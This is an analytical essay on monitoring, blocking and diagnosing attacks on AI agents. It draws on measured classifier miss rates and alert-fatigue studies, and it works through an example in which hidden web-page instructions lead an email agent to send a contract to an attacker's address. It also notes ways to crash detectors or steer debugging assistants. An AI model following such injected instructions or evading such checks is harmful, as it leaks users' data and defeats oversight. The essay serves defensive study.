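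The classifier works in two stages. A quick yes-or-no check flags anything doubtful, and a slower check then reasons about the flagged actions. Anthropic measured both stages on 10,000 real tool calls by its staff, 52 real actions that went beyond what the user had authorised, and 1,000 synthetic attempts to leak data:

| | Harmless calls blocked | Unauthorised actions missed | Synthetic leaks missed |
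|---|---|---|---|
| Quick check only | 8.5% | 6.6% | 1.8% |
| Both stages | 0.4% | 17% | 5.7% |

The slower check removed most false alarms but let more dangerous actions through. With only 52 unauthorised actions in the test, the true miss rate could plausibly be from about 9% to 30%. If the leak and false alarm rates applied to whole runs in the earlier example, the classifier would raise about 400 false alarms and nine true ones, a precision of about 2%.

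BestHub's *Can Claude Code's Auto Mode Replace Human Review?* summarises a study with less favourable results than Anthropic's. Across 253 actions in deliberately difficult scenarios, auto mode missed 81.0% of the risky actions and blocked 19.8% of the harmless ones. Part of the gap comes from actions that skip the classifier, such as edits to project files, but the miss rate was still 70.3% among the kinds of action that reach it. The exact figures deserve some caution because BestHub's account is second-hand, but they suggest that Anthropic's rates depend heavily on the mix of actions in its tests.

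### What too many alerts do to people

Security teams have worked with low-precision alerts for years. *True Attacks, Attack Attempts, or Benign Triggers?*, by Yang, Chen and colleagues, analysed 115 million network alerts generated between 2018 and 2022 at a supercomputing centre in Illinois. The nine-person security team received between 24,000 and 134,000 alerts a day, and only 0.01% of them related to successful attacks. From 2020, a system handled some alerts automatically, for instance by blocking the network address involved. Four of the 11 successful attacks in that period could not be detected from the alerts.

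The detector had worked correctly for many of the unhelpful alerts. Yang and colleagues classed 49% as "benign triggers", meaning that the rule had matched correctly but the activity had a legitimate reason. At least another 27% were attacks that had failed. Yang and colleagues took the idea of a benign trigger from *99% False Positives* (Alahmadi, Axon and Martinovic, 2022), an interview study in which analysts attributed most of what others call false positives to benign triggers. The alerts that a baseline of recipients would raise for new customers are benign triggers too.

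People who see many harmless warnings tend to stop looking closely. In a study for Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026), 1,053 paid testers did coding work in which Claude Code repeatedly asked for approval. Once per session, the researchers replaced a request with a clearly dangerous command. Only 13.6% of testers refused it. The refusal rate fell from about 17% early in a session to about 5% after 50 or more requests. Auto mode blocked 89% of the same commands, and its rate didn't fall over time.

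Anthropic was arguing for making auto mode the default, and the testers had less reason to be careful because they were not working on their own projects. In real use, though, people approve 97% of Claude Code's requests. That figure alone doesn't prove carelessness, since most of the requests are probably safe, but the decline within sessions is stronger evidence of it.

Ranking alerts can make better use of limited attention. Uetz, Bönninghausen and colleagues (2026), in *Can Risk-Based Alerting Mitigate Cybersecurity Alert Fatigue?*, found that a single security tool at one company had raised 15,060 alerts in a week. They scored an alert higher if it was severe, rare or not part of a regular pattern in time, or if the same machine had recently produced many alerts or several different kinds. Across eight sets of alerts, a true alert outranked a false one about 92% of the time, compared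 with 72% when they ranked by severity alone. Most of the data came from test networks, and none of it concerned AI agents. But the method suits the email agent, because reading an outside page, opening a contract and writing to a new address are each ordinary but suspicious when all three happen in one run.

Premise 2 looks false for individual alerts about possible attacks at the error rates researchers have measured so far, unless attacks are much more common than in the example. Developers would probably stop reading alerts that were right 1% or 2% of the time. The premise is more plausible for grouped or ranked alerts. It is also more plausible for posture findings, because unsafe settings are probably far more common than attacks and a tool can read them directly. A posture finding can still be a benign trigger if the developer had a good reason for the setting.

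### When blocking pays

A detector that is too imprecise for alerts can still be useful for blocking. Let p be the chance that a flagged action is an attack, L the loss if the attack succeeds, and C the cost of blocking a legitimate action. Allowing the action has an expected cost of pL. Blocking it has an expected cost of (1 − p)C, because blocking does harm only when the action was legitimate. Blocking is therefore cheaper when

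pL > (1 − p)C, or p > C / (C + L)

Suppose a wrongly blocked action costs $5 in delay and repeated work, and a successful attack costs $1,000. Blocking then saves money when p is above 5/1,005, or about 0.5%. In the first example p was 0.9%, so the company should block even though more than 99% of the blocks would be mistakes. Blocking would prevent $9,000 in losses a day, and the wrong blocks would cost about $5,000.

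In that case, human review would cost more than it saves. At $20 an alert, reviewing all 1,009 would cost about $20,000 and prevent at most $9,000 in losses, even if the reviewers made no mistakes. With a false alarm rate of 0.01%, reviewing 19 alerts would cost $380, far less than the losses it could prevent, but blocking all 19 automatically would still be cheaper. Review is cheaper than automatic blocking only when a wrong block costs more, for example because it delays a payment to an important supplier. At 47% precision, that cost, C, would have to exceed about $38.

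The result depends heavily on the number of attacks, which a company rarely knows. In the first example, blocking breaks even at between five and six attacked runs a day. At the same prices, the company would lose money by blocking if attackers targeted only one run a day.

Where the check takes place also matters. The calculation assumes that an attack would succeed if nobody blocked it. That is reasonable once the email agent has tried to send a contract to a stranger, but much less so when the research agent has only read a hostile page, because the model may ignore the instructions. In an evaluation that Anthropic commissioned from Trajectory Labs, a testing company, hidden instructions succeeded in only 0.09% of attempts against recent Claude models without permission checks, and in 19.03% against OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol with full access. The attacks had been optimised against an older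 Claude model, so the results aren't a fair comparison of the two companies' models. Even at a 19% success rate, the nine catches in the example would save only about $1,700 a day, so a company might reasonably log suspicious pages and block only suspicious actions.

### Checks that run before the action

To block an action, a platform has to intercept the tool call after the model has produced it and before the tool runs. Amazon does this at a gateway between agents and their tools. In June 2026, as AWS's *Amazon Bedrock AgentCore now supports Bedrock Guardrails in policy* (2026) announced, customers gained the ability to use guardrail results in the policies that decide which actions an agent may take. For the leaking email, the process would be:

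1. The email agent's program sends the `send_email` call to the gateway.
2. A guardrail checks the call's inputs for prompt injection, harmful content and sensitive information.
3. The policy combines the guardrail's result with its other rules and allows or refuses the call.
4. If the policy refuses, the mail tool never receives the call. The gateway logs the decision either way.

The guardrail also checks what tools return, so it might have stopped the poisoned page earlier. Because the gateway is separate from the agent's code, a hijacked agent can't simply skip the check unless it has another route to the mail server.

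Foundry's guardrails can act at the same two points, and slbird listed task adherence and sensitive-data detection among the controls in the 2025 preview. A task-adherence check might have flagged emailing a contract as unnecessary for finding delivery terms.

Microsoft Defender adds a check that security teams control. Microsoft announced it in preview for the Agent 365 tooling gateway in April 2026. A webhook sends Defender details of the action an agent is about to take, and Defender can block a malicious or risky action before it runs.

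Some checks don't have to estimate whether something is an attack. Help Net Security's *Arcjet brings security controls and audit trails to AI agents* describes a product that lets a company restrict the recipients or attachments an email tool accepts. If an email violates a restriction, the application can stop the action, ask a person or explain the problem to the agent. A list of permitted recipients would have stopped the leak without recognising the attack. It would also stop legitimate messages to anyone missing from the list, so it suits an agent that writes to the same few people better than one that answers the public.

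### Added delay and failed checks

The agent has to wait for each check. The run in the email example took about 15 seconds and included four tool calls, so a half-second check on each call would add two seconds. Checking only `send_email` would add half a second and could still prevent the leak. AWS and Microsoft gave no delay figures in their announcements, so customers will have to measure the delay themselves.

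Anthropic reduces the delay by running the slower check only on actions that the quick one has flagged. It also lets Claude Code read files and edit the current project without running the classifier. Such exemptions save time, but BestHub's figures suggest that they create gaps in coverage.

If a checker crashes or takes too long to answer, the platform can "fail open", which lets actions continue unchecked, or "fail closed", which stops them. AWS and Microsoft did not state in their announcements which their platforms do. In Claude Code, a session that should use auto mode starts in manual approval if auto mode isn't available, according to the *Claude Code Complete User Handbook* (2026). This may protect users less than it appears to, because testers rarely refused dangerous commands.

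Developers can also use the blocking rule to decide what an agent should do when the detector is down. In the example, 1 in 10,000 runs is under attack, so the expected loss from an unchecked run is $0.10. Stopping the run costs $5. Failing open, which means letting the run continue unchecked, is therefore cheaper unless a successful attack would cost more than about $50,000. But this assumes that the outage is unrelated to the attack. An attacker who can crash the detector, perhaps by flooding it with requests, can do so just before sending the malicious instructions. It makes sense for an agent to fail closed on messages that send documents outside the company and fail open on low-risk steps such as checking a calendar. Developers can switch off the detector in a test environment to find out whether their platform fails open or closed.

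### Blocking first or observing first

Blocking from the first day makes the most sense for actions that nobody can undo. An alert about the leaked contract does little to prevent the leak if it arrives after the email has gone. Blocking also saves about $4,000 a day at the assumed costs, so two weeks of only watching would cost the company about $56,000.

Wrong blocks can also cause little disruption. When auto mode blocks an action, it gives Claude Code the reason and lets it look for a safer way to do the task. After three blocks in a row or 20 in a session, it asks the user to step in. Anthropic argues that a false alarm therefore usually results in one retry. An agent with only one way to complete its task, such as sending a particular email, would benefit less from the chance to retry.

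It makes sense to observe a detector before letting it block, because a company doesn't know how it will behave on the company's own traffic. ProtectAI v2 rarely flagged ordinary web pages, but using it to block could have stopped 69% of the harmless tasks in Liu's AgentDojo test. A team that saw similar results in production might turn off blocking altogether. Counting blocks once the detector is live won't reveal the problem. Anthropic reports that about 10% of sessions at Gusto, a customer, included a blocked action, and presents this as evidence that auto mode was doing useful work, but the figure doesn't show how many of those blocks were correct.

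A company can observe first by running the detector on live traffic and recording what it would have blocked, without stopping the agent. Someone then checks a sample of the flagged runs. Collecting enough harmless traffic to test for a 0.01% false alarm rate would take hours at 100,000 runs a day, but about five months at 200 runs a day. The developer of the less-used agent would have to accept a less certain estimate or replay old runs.

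There are also options between blocking an action and only recording it. *Shall We Approve?* (2026), a study of approval for coding agents, describes undoing a blocked command and returning the reason to the agent. It compares this with YoloFS, a system that blocks nothing and holds the agent's changes for the user to inspect or reverse. A sent email can't be reversed, but the mail tool could hold messages to new recipients for a few minutes while a slower detector examines the run.

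Companies can choose whether to alert or block separately for each check. A rule that contracts may go only to approved recipients can block immediately, because the developer can predict what it will stop. An injection detector should usually run in observation mode until the company has measured its false alarms. If the agent handles documents whose loss would be very expensive, the developer can require approval for outgoing attachments during that period, as long as there are few enough requests for people to read them properly.

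## What lets a developer act on a signal

A developer may receive a correct alert and still not know which agent it concerns, which step went wrong or what to change. Repairs depend on what the signal contains, how many of the fixes a developer can make (Premise 3), and whether developers respond more often to signals that appear where they work (Premise 4).

### Four conditions for an actionable signal

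An actionable signal reaches someone able to fix the cause, with enough evidence to find it. In practice, it has to meet four conditions:

1. It names the agent, the version that was running and the owner.
2. It points to the step that failed.
3. It shows the evidence.
4. It leads to a setting that the recipient may change.

The following invented alert about the email leak meets none of them:

```
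HIGH       Suspicious AI activity
Resource:  ai-prod-02
Time:      10:42
Action:    Review your AI applications
```

The developer would have to find out which agents run on that resource, search their traces around 10:42 and guess which of several ordinary-looking runs caused the alert. Many developers would close it. A better alert about the same event might look like this:

```
HIGH       Contract sent to an address taken from a web page
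Agent:     email-agent, version 12
Owner:     purchasing tools team
Run:       conversation c-4471, step send_email
Evidence:  fetch_page read supplier-terms.example (untrusted)
           research-agent's answer repeated x@attacker.example
           email-agent's program treated the answer as trusted
           send_email attached contract.pdf
Unknown:   whether other agents have read the page
Change:    allowed recipients for send_email (owner can edit)
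```

The headline describes what happened and leaves out speculation about the cause. The owner is a team because an individual may have changed jobs since building the agent. The developer can use the version to identify which later releases to check for the same fault.

A posture finding has no failed step to point to, so it should identify the risky setting. The permissions widget that Google Cloud describes comes fairly close, because it lists specific agent identities and the permissions each one doesn't use. But if only an administrator can change an agent's role, the developer who sees the finding can't act on it.

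### Repairs a developer can make

For the email leak, the developer could make any of five kinds of change:

| Change | In the email example | Main weakness |
|---|---|---|
| Instructions | Tell the email agent never to follow instructions in the research agent's answers | The model may follow them anyway |
| Tool scope | Remove file search from runs that read outside text | Some legitimate tasks need both |
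| Permissions | Let the agent write only to approved recipients | New customers need approval first |
| Guardrail settings | Check the research agent's answers for injection | The check will miss some attacks and block some harmless text |
| Rollback | Return to version 11 | Version 11 may have the same fault |

Giving the agent new instructions is the quickest fix but probably the least reliable. If the agent writes to a fairly stable group of people, limiting who it can write to is the better first fix.

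Rollback works well when a recent release caused the problem, for example by adding the mail tool. But it can't recall a sent email, and it may not remove a hostile instruction that the agent has saved to long-term memory, so the developer needs to check the memory separately.

Other repairs require people besides the developer. If an attacker has stolen an agent's credentials, an identity administrator has to revoke them and the security operations team has to find out where else the attacker used them. Removing a password from the code doesn't stop an attacker from using a stolen copy. If the flaw is in a vendor's model or platform, the developer can switch off the affected tool while waiting for the vendor's fix. If the leaked contract contained personal data, lawyers may have to decide whether the company must notify a regulator or the people affected, and the developer needs to tell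 the lawyers accurately what left the company and when.

Premise 3 therefore looks true for most posture findings and guardrail events, and for goal hijacks like the email leak. It is weaker for threat detections that involve stolen tokens or powerful roles. Nobody seems to have counted how many real agent incidents each party could have fixed, so the claim of "many" rests mainly on examples.

Research on ordinary agent failures gives a rough idea of which problems developers can act on. In *TRAIL* (Deshpande, Gangal and colleagues, 2025), people labeled 841 errors in 148 agent traces. About 42% were formatting errors or failures to follow instructions, which a developer can often reduce by changing prompts or tool descriptions. That share may be lower in normal use, because the researchers added restrictive instructions to one of their two agent systems to provoke mistakes. Failures in the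 surrounding system, such as missing API keys and rate limits, were rare.

### What counts as the faulty step

A leak can involve several mistakes, so "the step that failed" needs a definition. Zhang, Yin and colleagues (2025), in *Which Agent Causes Task Failures and When?*, base theirs on what would have happened without each mistake. Let Z(τ) be 1 if a run τ fails and 0 if it succeeds. Let τ′ be the run that would have followed if one agent had acted correctly at step t, with the later steps adjusted to fit. The mistake at step t is decisive if

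Z(τ) = 1 and Z(τ′) = 0

If a run contains several decisive mistakes, the definition picks the earliest.

For security, the difficulty is deciding what counts as failure. The user who asked for delivery terms may well have received them, and a check of the task alone would then give Z = 0, leaving no failure to explain. *A Survey on AgentOps* (Wang, Li and colleagues, 2025) calls the definition too limited, partly because a run can finish successfully even though something went wrong. A security team can fix this by also counting a run as failed if the agent breaks a rule, for example by sending a contract to a stranger.

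Under that rule, the earliest decisive mistake in the leak was probably the research agent's answer, which passed on the hidden instructions. But the most dependable fix is to limit `send_email`, which comes several steps later in a different agent. An alert should therefore show the path from the cause to the harm, because the owner of the agent that made the first mistake may not be the person best able to prevent the next leak.

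### How well people find the faulty step

People can usually find the step where a run went wrong, but it takes them a long time. Zhang's team asked three experts to label 184 failed runs of multi-agent systems. The experts spent about 84 hours, or 27 minutes per failure, and were initially unsure about 15–30% of their labels. They sometimes had to revisit the websites an agent had read to find out whether the information was missing or the agent had overlooked it.

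For *TRAIL*, labelling all the errors in a trace took 30 to 40 minutes, or about two hours with four rounds of checking. Reviewers changed the labels on 5–6% of the steps they checked. Agreement might have been lower if they had labelled the traces from scratch.

At half an hour per trace, reviewing an alert could easily cost more than the $20 assumed earlier if the developer has to find the faulty step. Automatic fault location is therefore attractive even if it is only moderately accurate.

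### How well models find it

Zhang's team turned the 184 failures into a benchmark called Who&When and tested GPT-4o on it in several ways. One method gave the model the whole log at once. Another gave it one step at a time until it flagged a mistake. The paper's two headline results, 53.5% accuracy for naming the responsible agent and 14.2% for naming the exact step, come from different methods. The method that was best at naming the agent did worse than random guessing at naming the step.

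Later systems have done much better:

| Method | Model | Correct agent | Exact step |
|---|---|---|---|
| Random guess | None | 20.6% | 11.6% |
| Whole log at once | GPT-4o | 53.5% | 8.7% |
| One step at a time | GPT-4o | 32.1% | 14.2% |
| Whole log at once | GLM-5.2 | 62.5% | 17.9% |
| One step at a time | GLM-5.2 | 46.7% | 27.2% |
| FAMAS, which compares repeated runs | None | 57.6% | 29.3% |
| DeFA | GLM-5.2 | 72.3% | 52.7% |

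The first three rows are averages of Zhang and colleagues' results, weighting hand-built and automatically generated agent systems equally. The FAMAS figures come from *Cascade Failure Attribution for Multi-Agent Systems* (2026) and the GLM-5.2 figures from *DeFA* (Deng, Zheng and colleagues, 2026). Both papers pooled all 184 failures, which raises step scores slightly because most of the logs are short ones from generated systems.

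DeFA has an advantage because it follows information through the run. A model links each step to the later steps that used its content. It then lists suspicious steps, traces where each problem came from and what it affected, and chooses the mistake whose correction would have made the run succeed. In one example, a web agent retrieved a table of films, an assistant left one film out of a comparison, and a later step reported the wrong total. DeFA correctly identified the comparison as the source of the error.

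The same approach suits the email leak, although DeFA has to infer the links between steps from the text. A platform that records provenance already has many of those links, so finding the source of an address could be more like looking it up than making a judgement. The results above don't show how much recorded provenance would help.

Long runs are still difficult. The hand-built system's runs average 52 turns and reach 130, according to *Can Failed Trajectories Reveal Where Agents Go Wrong?* (2026), while the generated systems' runs have at most ten. All three of the original methods fell close to 0% on the longest logs. *TRAJDEBUG* (2026) reports that its own method, the best it tested, averaged 34% across several benchmarks but only 24% on software tasks with an average of about 120 steps.

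### Reading one step at a time

*TRAIL* sets a harder task, because a model has to find every error in a trace and classify it by type. In 2025 the best model, Gemini 2.5 Pro, found and correctly classified 18% of the errors in web-research traces and 5% of those in software traces. Some traces were too long for the models to read.

In *Holistic Evaluation and Failure Diagnosis of AI Agents*, Madvil, Dym and colleagues (2026) later tested GPT-5.4 on the same traces. Given a whole trace, the model located errors with 29% accuracy on web research and 7% on software. When their framework had it judge the steps separately, accuracy rose to 82% and 86%. The researchers work for Deepchecks, which sells evaluation software, but they used the same model in both tests, and the gain is very large.

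The figures are less impressive than they look. Madvil's team defines accuracy as the share of flagged steps that the human annotators had also marked, so it ignores errors the model missed. The annotators also marked so many steps that, by the counts in *TRAIL*, picking steps at random would score about 39% on web research and 19% on software. The labels are also inconsistent, because the annotators sometimes blamed a faulty tool call on the model that wrote it and sometimes on the tool that received it.

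Judging steps separately may also work less well for an attack like the email leak, where most steps look ordinary on their own. The Deepchecks framework can include neighbouring steps and judge the run as a whole, and a security version would depend heavily on those features.

Weaker set-ups do badly even on the same data. *Structural Baselines Matter for Agent Failure Detection and Attribution* (2026) gave GPT-4o each step's name, status and attributes from the *TRAIL* traces. GPT-4o never named the exact target step and came within two steps of it on only 18% of traces.

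### Planted errors and real ones

DeFA scored up to 80% on Who&When Pro, a newer benchmark in which researchers insert a mistake into a run. Xu and Gao (2026) show in *Auditing Failure Attribution* why such scores should be read with caution. They trained a simple classifier on the words in an agent's reasoning and showed it only one step at a time, so it could not compare steps. It found the inserted mistake in 95–100% of runs from two agent systems, while GPT-4.1 found it in 59% of runs from one of those systems.

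Models that hadn't trained on the benchmark's answers mostly ignored one of the cues Xu and Gao studied, so DeFA's score may still reflect real checking. But planted mistakes can be easier to recognise than natural ones. On another benchmark, a similar classifier found 66% of planted failures but only 20% of natural ones. A company that tests a fault finder only on attacks staged by its own staff could likewise overestimate how well it works on real attacks.

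Most of these tests also start with a run known to have failed, whereas a developer investigating an alert may be looking at a harmless one. *Locating Hidden Failures Makes Long-Horizon Agents More Reliable* (2026) introduces Traverse, a benchmark that includes correct runs as well as natural failures. None of the benchmarks described here was built to measure how well a model explains prompt injection.

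Given these error rates, an alert should present the suspected step as a suggestion and link it to the evidence. The developer can then reject a wrong suggestion in a minute or two instead of rewriting the wrong agent's prompt. Suggestions can be more useful when combined across many runs. On the hand-built system, all three of Zhang's original methods correctly identified the agent that caused the most failures overall, even though they were often wrong about individual runs. That would help a team decide which agent to examine first, but it wouldn't explain a one-time leak.

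### Turning an incident into a test

A recorded incident can become a regression test, which checks that a fault hasn't returned. For the email leak, the developer could build one as follows:

1. Save the web page's text, the user's request and the settings of both agents. Replace the real contract with a dummy.
2. Connect the agents to fake tools. The fake `fetch_page` returns the saved page, and the fake `send_email` records messages without sending them.
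3. Run version 12 and confirm that the leak happens again.
4. Run version 13 and check that no message goes to an address the user hasn't approved.
5. Add a legitimate request, such as sending the contract to an approved customer. Otherwise an agent that refuses every request would pass.
6. Repeat the test before each release.

Step 3 also checks the diagnosis. If version 12 doesn't leak with the saved page, the record may be incomplete, or the model may follow the instructions only occasionally. If it does leak, and changing a single setting stops the leak, the developer has good evidence that the setting mattered.

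Models vary from run to run, so one pass proves little. If a flawed version leaks with probability q on each run, the chance that it passes n independent runs is

(1 − q)ⁿ

If a flaw causes a failure in 10% of runs (q = 10%), a flawed version would pass ten runs about 35% of the time. The developer would need 29 runs to bring that below 5%. A fix in the permissions is much easier to test because, without running the model, the developer can send a forbidden recipient directly to the program that enforces the limit and check that it refuses.

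The test should also include reworded versions of the hidden instructions, since a guardrail might recognise only the wording on the saved page. The fake tools also need some flexibility, because if version 13 searches for something that version 12 didn't, the recording will have no result to return and the test could fail for a reason unrelated to security.

In *Mind the Metrics*, Koc, Verre and colleagues (2025) propose running such checks in continuous integration, the automated tests that run whenever a developer changes a program. Their system would use stored traces and measurements to catch regressions and refine prompts. They work for Comet, which sells tracing software, and they present a design without experiments. The practice still makes sense because it uses an incident the company has already investigated.

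### Coding assistants that read traces

An AI coding assistant can do some of this work if it can access the traces. In Koc's design, the assistant runs in the developer's code editor and fetches traces and test results through MCP. The developer could ask why the email agent wrote to a stranger, and the assistant could find the run, suggest a change and test it without the developer opening a dashboard.

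Some evidence suggests that automatic diagnoses help improve agents. Deng and colleagues fed DeFA's diagnoses into Trace2Skill, a method that turns lessons from past runs into reusable instructions. Accuracy on later tasks was 6 to 15 percentage points higher than with Trace2Skill alone. The experiment measured task accuracy, so it doesn't show that the instructions made agents safer. *TraceSIR* (2026), which uses several agents to turn traces into written reports, warns that the quality of the analysis may depend on the underlying model. It also assumes a moderate number of runs, so it may not handle a large company's full traffic.

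The trace of the leak contains the attacker's instructions, which the assistant has to read to explain what happened, a risk that ordinary debugging doesn't have. This exposes it to the same kind of attack as the email agent. The instructions might lead it to dismiss the alert, blame the wrong agent or propose a change that weakens a guardrail. The assistant may also be a more valuable target, because it can often read source code and run commands.

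Labelling the text as untrusted helps, but doesn't reliably stop a model from following instructions in it. Limiting what the assistant can do is safer. A company can give the trace to a model that has no tools and returns only a few fixed fields, such as the suspected step and the setting involved. If those fields don't allow free text, a second assistant can draft the change without receiving the attacker's text. The second assistant may write a worse fix because it has less information about the incident.

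A person should still compare the proposed change with the original evidence, and the regression test should run before release. Koc's team also describes monitoring agents that rewrite prompts without direct human intervention. If the monitored agent reads outside text, an attacker could use the trace of a single bad run to influence its permanent instructions.

### Whether placement changes what developers do

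The best evidence for Premise 4 comes from static analysis, in which software looks for bugs in code without running it. In *Scaling Static Analyses at Facebook*, Distefano, Fähndrich and colleagues (2019) describe two ways of delivering findings from the same tool, Infer. At first, Infer ran overnight on Facebook's Android code, and the team assigned 20 to 30 of its findings to the developers who seemed best placed to fix them. The developers fixed almost none. The team then had Infer comment on code changes during review, and the fix rate rose to over 70%, although the false alarm rate stayed the same.

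Distefano's team gives two reasons why a bug reported at code review is easier to act on than an old one. A developer who receives an old bug has to stop other tasks and remember how the code works, while a comment at review concerns code the developer has just written. The right person to fix the bug is also easy to find at review, because the author of the change is already taking part.

*Lessons from Building Static Analysis Tools at Google* (Sadowski, Aftandilian and colleagues, 2018) describes a similar experience with a tool called FindBugs. Developers rarely used a dashboard of its nightly findings because it was outside their normal workflow. In 2009, hundreds of engineers spent a week reviewing 3,954 warnings. They filed bug reports for 44% but fixed only 16%, which suggests that filing a bug report often doesn't lead to a fix. Google then showed FindBugs results in code review,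 but even there false alarms made developers lose trust in the tool, and Google dropped the integration in 2011.

Both studies are about code analysis, and neither was a controlled experiment. Facebook's overnight findings were few and concerned existing code, which is harder to change than the new code its review comments covered. Still, the rise from almost zero to over 70% is too large to dismiss.

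No published study from 2025 or 2026 seems to measure how developers handle security alerts about agents. The closest match to a review comment is a posture finding that appears while a developer is editing an agent, such as a warning that version 13 can write to anyone. Another good match is the sensitive-data warning that Microsoft describes, which appears during testing. Premise 4 is plausible for both.

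It is much less certain that developers will act on alerts from live agents. A leak may happen months after the developer last changed the agent, so the developer has to recall how it works, as with Facebook's overnight findings. An alert on a security tab is also more like Google's neglected dashboard than a review comment, even if the tab is on the platform where the developer built the agent. A company could make developers more likely to act by attaching the alert to a proposed change and a failing regression test. The developer would then see the problem in code review, along with the evidence and a possible fix.

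## Who may read the records

The trace that explains the email leak can also contain the leaked contract, the user's other messages and any password someone pasted into them. A developer can often repair an agent without reading anyone's email, so whether the benefits of developer signals outweigh the risk of exposing this data (Premise 5) depends on what the platform shows developers.

### Private text in a trace

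Kong warns users of its gateway that the fields for model inputs and outputs may contain personal data, secrets or credentials. The problem is especially bad for an email agent, which handles messages that people did not write for the agent's developer to read. A customer might mention an illness to explain a late payment, an employee might complain about a manager, and a supplier's draft contract might reveal prices that a competitor would like to know.

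The evidence of an attack is often in the same field as the private text. The model input that contains an attacker's hidden instructions also contains the user's request and whatever else the agent has read, so a platform can't show the whole field to developers without showing them the private text.

However, many developers can probably read this text already. tianpan.co's *The AI Observability Leak* (2026), a practitioner's opinion piece, claims that hosted tracing tools capture entire requests and responses by default. In its example, an engineer connected such a tool during a hackathon, and the service kept unredacted data for 400 days. The article blames divided responsibility within companies. Legal staff handle the contracts and security staff write the data classification rules, but no single team checks what leaves the company. If this is common, adding a security alert to a trace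 that the developer can already open would expose little additional private data, but developers' existing access would often be too wide.

### Five ways to limit what developers see

Platforms can restrict the text in several ways, and each takes something away from an investigation:

| Design | What the email agent's developer could read | Main cost to the investigation |
|---|---|---|
| No message text | The steps, tool names and agent version | The trace contains neither the hidden instructions nor the recipient |
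| Masked text | The instructions, with names and addresses replaced | Masking may remove the attacker's address |
| Text in a separate store | The steps at once, the text after approval | Delay |
| Suspicious segment only | The passage that the detector picked out | The surrounding text may be missing |
| Nothing kept unless a detector finds an incident | The finding, if there is one | No evidence of attacks that the detector missed |

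OpenTelemetry's conventions leave message text out by default. In its *LLM call examples*, a user asks a model for a joke. With content capture off, the span still records the trace identifier, the provider and the model, but not the joke. An agent's span can also include the agent's version and the conversation identifier, according to OpenTelemetry. The email agent's developer could get the recipient from the mail server's log, but would still not know why the agent sent the message. Turning on content capture after the leak would help only if the attacker tried again.

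The conventions make a tool's arguments a separate optional field, so a tracing tool could record who the email agent wrote to without recording the whole conversation. But the arguments may include the body of the email, and OpenTelemetry warns that they can be sensitive too.

### Masking and how it fails

Masking replaces sensitive text before the platform stores it. A simple rule that turns every email address into "[email]" would protect customers but also erase the attacker's address, which links the web page to the outgoing message.

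Giving each address its own code works better. If the code E17 appears on the web page, in the research agent's answer and in the arguments of `send_email`, the developer can follow the address through the run without learning what it is. The company should derive the codes with a secret key. Otherwise, anyone who knows the method could compute the code for a colleague's address and search for it. Masking removes only what matches its rules, so a sentence about a customer's illness would probably remain.

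Masking software can miss text even when the developer has configured it correctly. GitLab's *Advisories for Npm/Langsmith package* describes a flaw in the library for LangSmith, LangChain's tracing service. The library had a setting to hide a model's outputs, but when a model streamed its answer in pieces, the library recorded each piece as a separate event and didn't apply the setting to those events. A developer who checked the output field would have seen that the text was gone, but the same trace still contained a full copy.

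Developers can easily test for this. They put a made-up password in a test message, run the agent once with streaming on and once with it off, and then search for that password in everything the tracing service stored, including events, error messages and guardrail results.

### Keeping the text in a separate store

For production systems with sensitive data, OpenTelemetry recommends storing the text outside the trace and putting only a reference to it on the span. The company can then let developers open the trace but require separate permission to read the text. OpenTelemetry suggests recording text directly on spans mainly in settings, such as testing before release, where privacy rules don't apply or the trace storage complies with them.

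A company can combine this design with masking. The conventions allow for a hook, which is code supplied by the company that receives the text of each model call. The hook can save the full text in the restricted store and then mask the copy that goes on the span. Developers would see the masked trace immediately, and an investigator could request the original.

OpenTelemetry says the hook should run whether or not the company keeps the trace. The text of a leak would then survive even if sampling discarded its trace. But the company would also store text from every harmless run, which conflicts with collecting as little as possible. It could instead have the hook save text only from risky runs. OpenTelemetry also hasn't settled how a span should refer to text stored elsewhere, so developers may have to build that link themselves.

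The main drawback is delay. If the email agent is leaking contracts at night and the one person who can grant access is asleep, the developer has to work without the text. Many companies handle this in other systems with emergency access, which lets a developer open a restricted record immediately for a limited time and notifies someone who reviews the access afterwards. The developer could also stop the email agent's outgoing attachments before reading anything.

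### Showing only the suspicious part

Microsoft's *Enable threat protection for AI services* describes a Defender setting called "user prompt evidence" that lets alerts include suspicious segments of users' prompts or the model's responses. A reader can then judge a jailbreak alert by the words that triggered it, without opening the rest of the conversation.

The detector selects the segment, so if it misses the hidden instructions, the developer gets no segment to read. Even if it finds them, the segment may leave out the user's request, which the developer needs to rule out that the user asked for the email. Microsoft defines the evidence as prompts and model responses. In the email leak, the instructions arrived through a tool, so the segment might show what the agent did with them but not the page they came from.

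A segment can also expose what the company wants to protect. When an alert concerns a password in a response, the segment may well be the password itself. Masking it would fix this with little loss of useful information, because the developer only needs to know that the agent revealed a password.

Microsoft's products can still keep prompts when prompt evidence is turned off, because a separate setting on the same screen lets Purview store prompts and responses for audits, legal searches and investigations of employees. A company that wants to limit how much text it keeps has to check both settings.

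### Keeping nothing without an incident

Google's Agent Platform Threat Detection discards its data on harmless runs. This protects users well but leaves no data from those runs to search when a new attack is discovered. The missing data probably matters less here than it would for a service that looked for prompt injection, because this one looks mainly for malicious programs.

The practice covers only the data that this service collects itself. Google Cloud's control-plane detectors read separate logs. If the developer's code prints each prompt to the output log while debugging, the prompts stay there as long as the company keeps that log, regardless of what the threat detector deletes. Google's anomaly detection requires traces with full text, so a customer who turns on both services loses much of the privacy that the threat detector offers.

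### Who can read what in practice

Anyone with access to a Foundry project can see its guardrail violations. However, Microsoft says that someone who opens an interaction in Purview from Foundry can see the prompt and response only if they belong to the Content Explorer Content Viewer role group.

Purview's audit log records when and how someone used an AI application. It can also identify the Microsoft 365 files that the application opened and any sensitivity labels on them. For the email leak, the log could show that the agent had opened a contract labelled confidential, without showing the contract itself. An investigator could then judge how serious the leak was before asking to read any of the content.

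People whom developers don't expect may also have access. Microsoft stores the prompts and responses in the user's mailbox, where legal staff can search them for evidence in a case. Defender's prompt evidence appears in the Azure portal, the Defender portal and any partner products the customer has connected. An outside monitoring firm that receives a company's alerts may therefore also receive parts of employees' conversations.

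A finding can need protection even if it contains no personal data. The integration between Defender and GitHub Code Security uses role-based access controls so that only authorised people can view findings and act on them. Microsoft gives responsible disclosure as the reason, since the findings include real and potential vulnerabilities that have not been fixed. The same reasoning applies to findings about agents. A dishonest employee who read a posture finding that the email agent follows instructions in web pages and can write to anyone could use it to steal a document and make the theft look like an outside attack.

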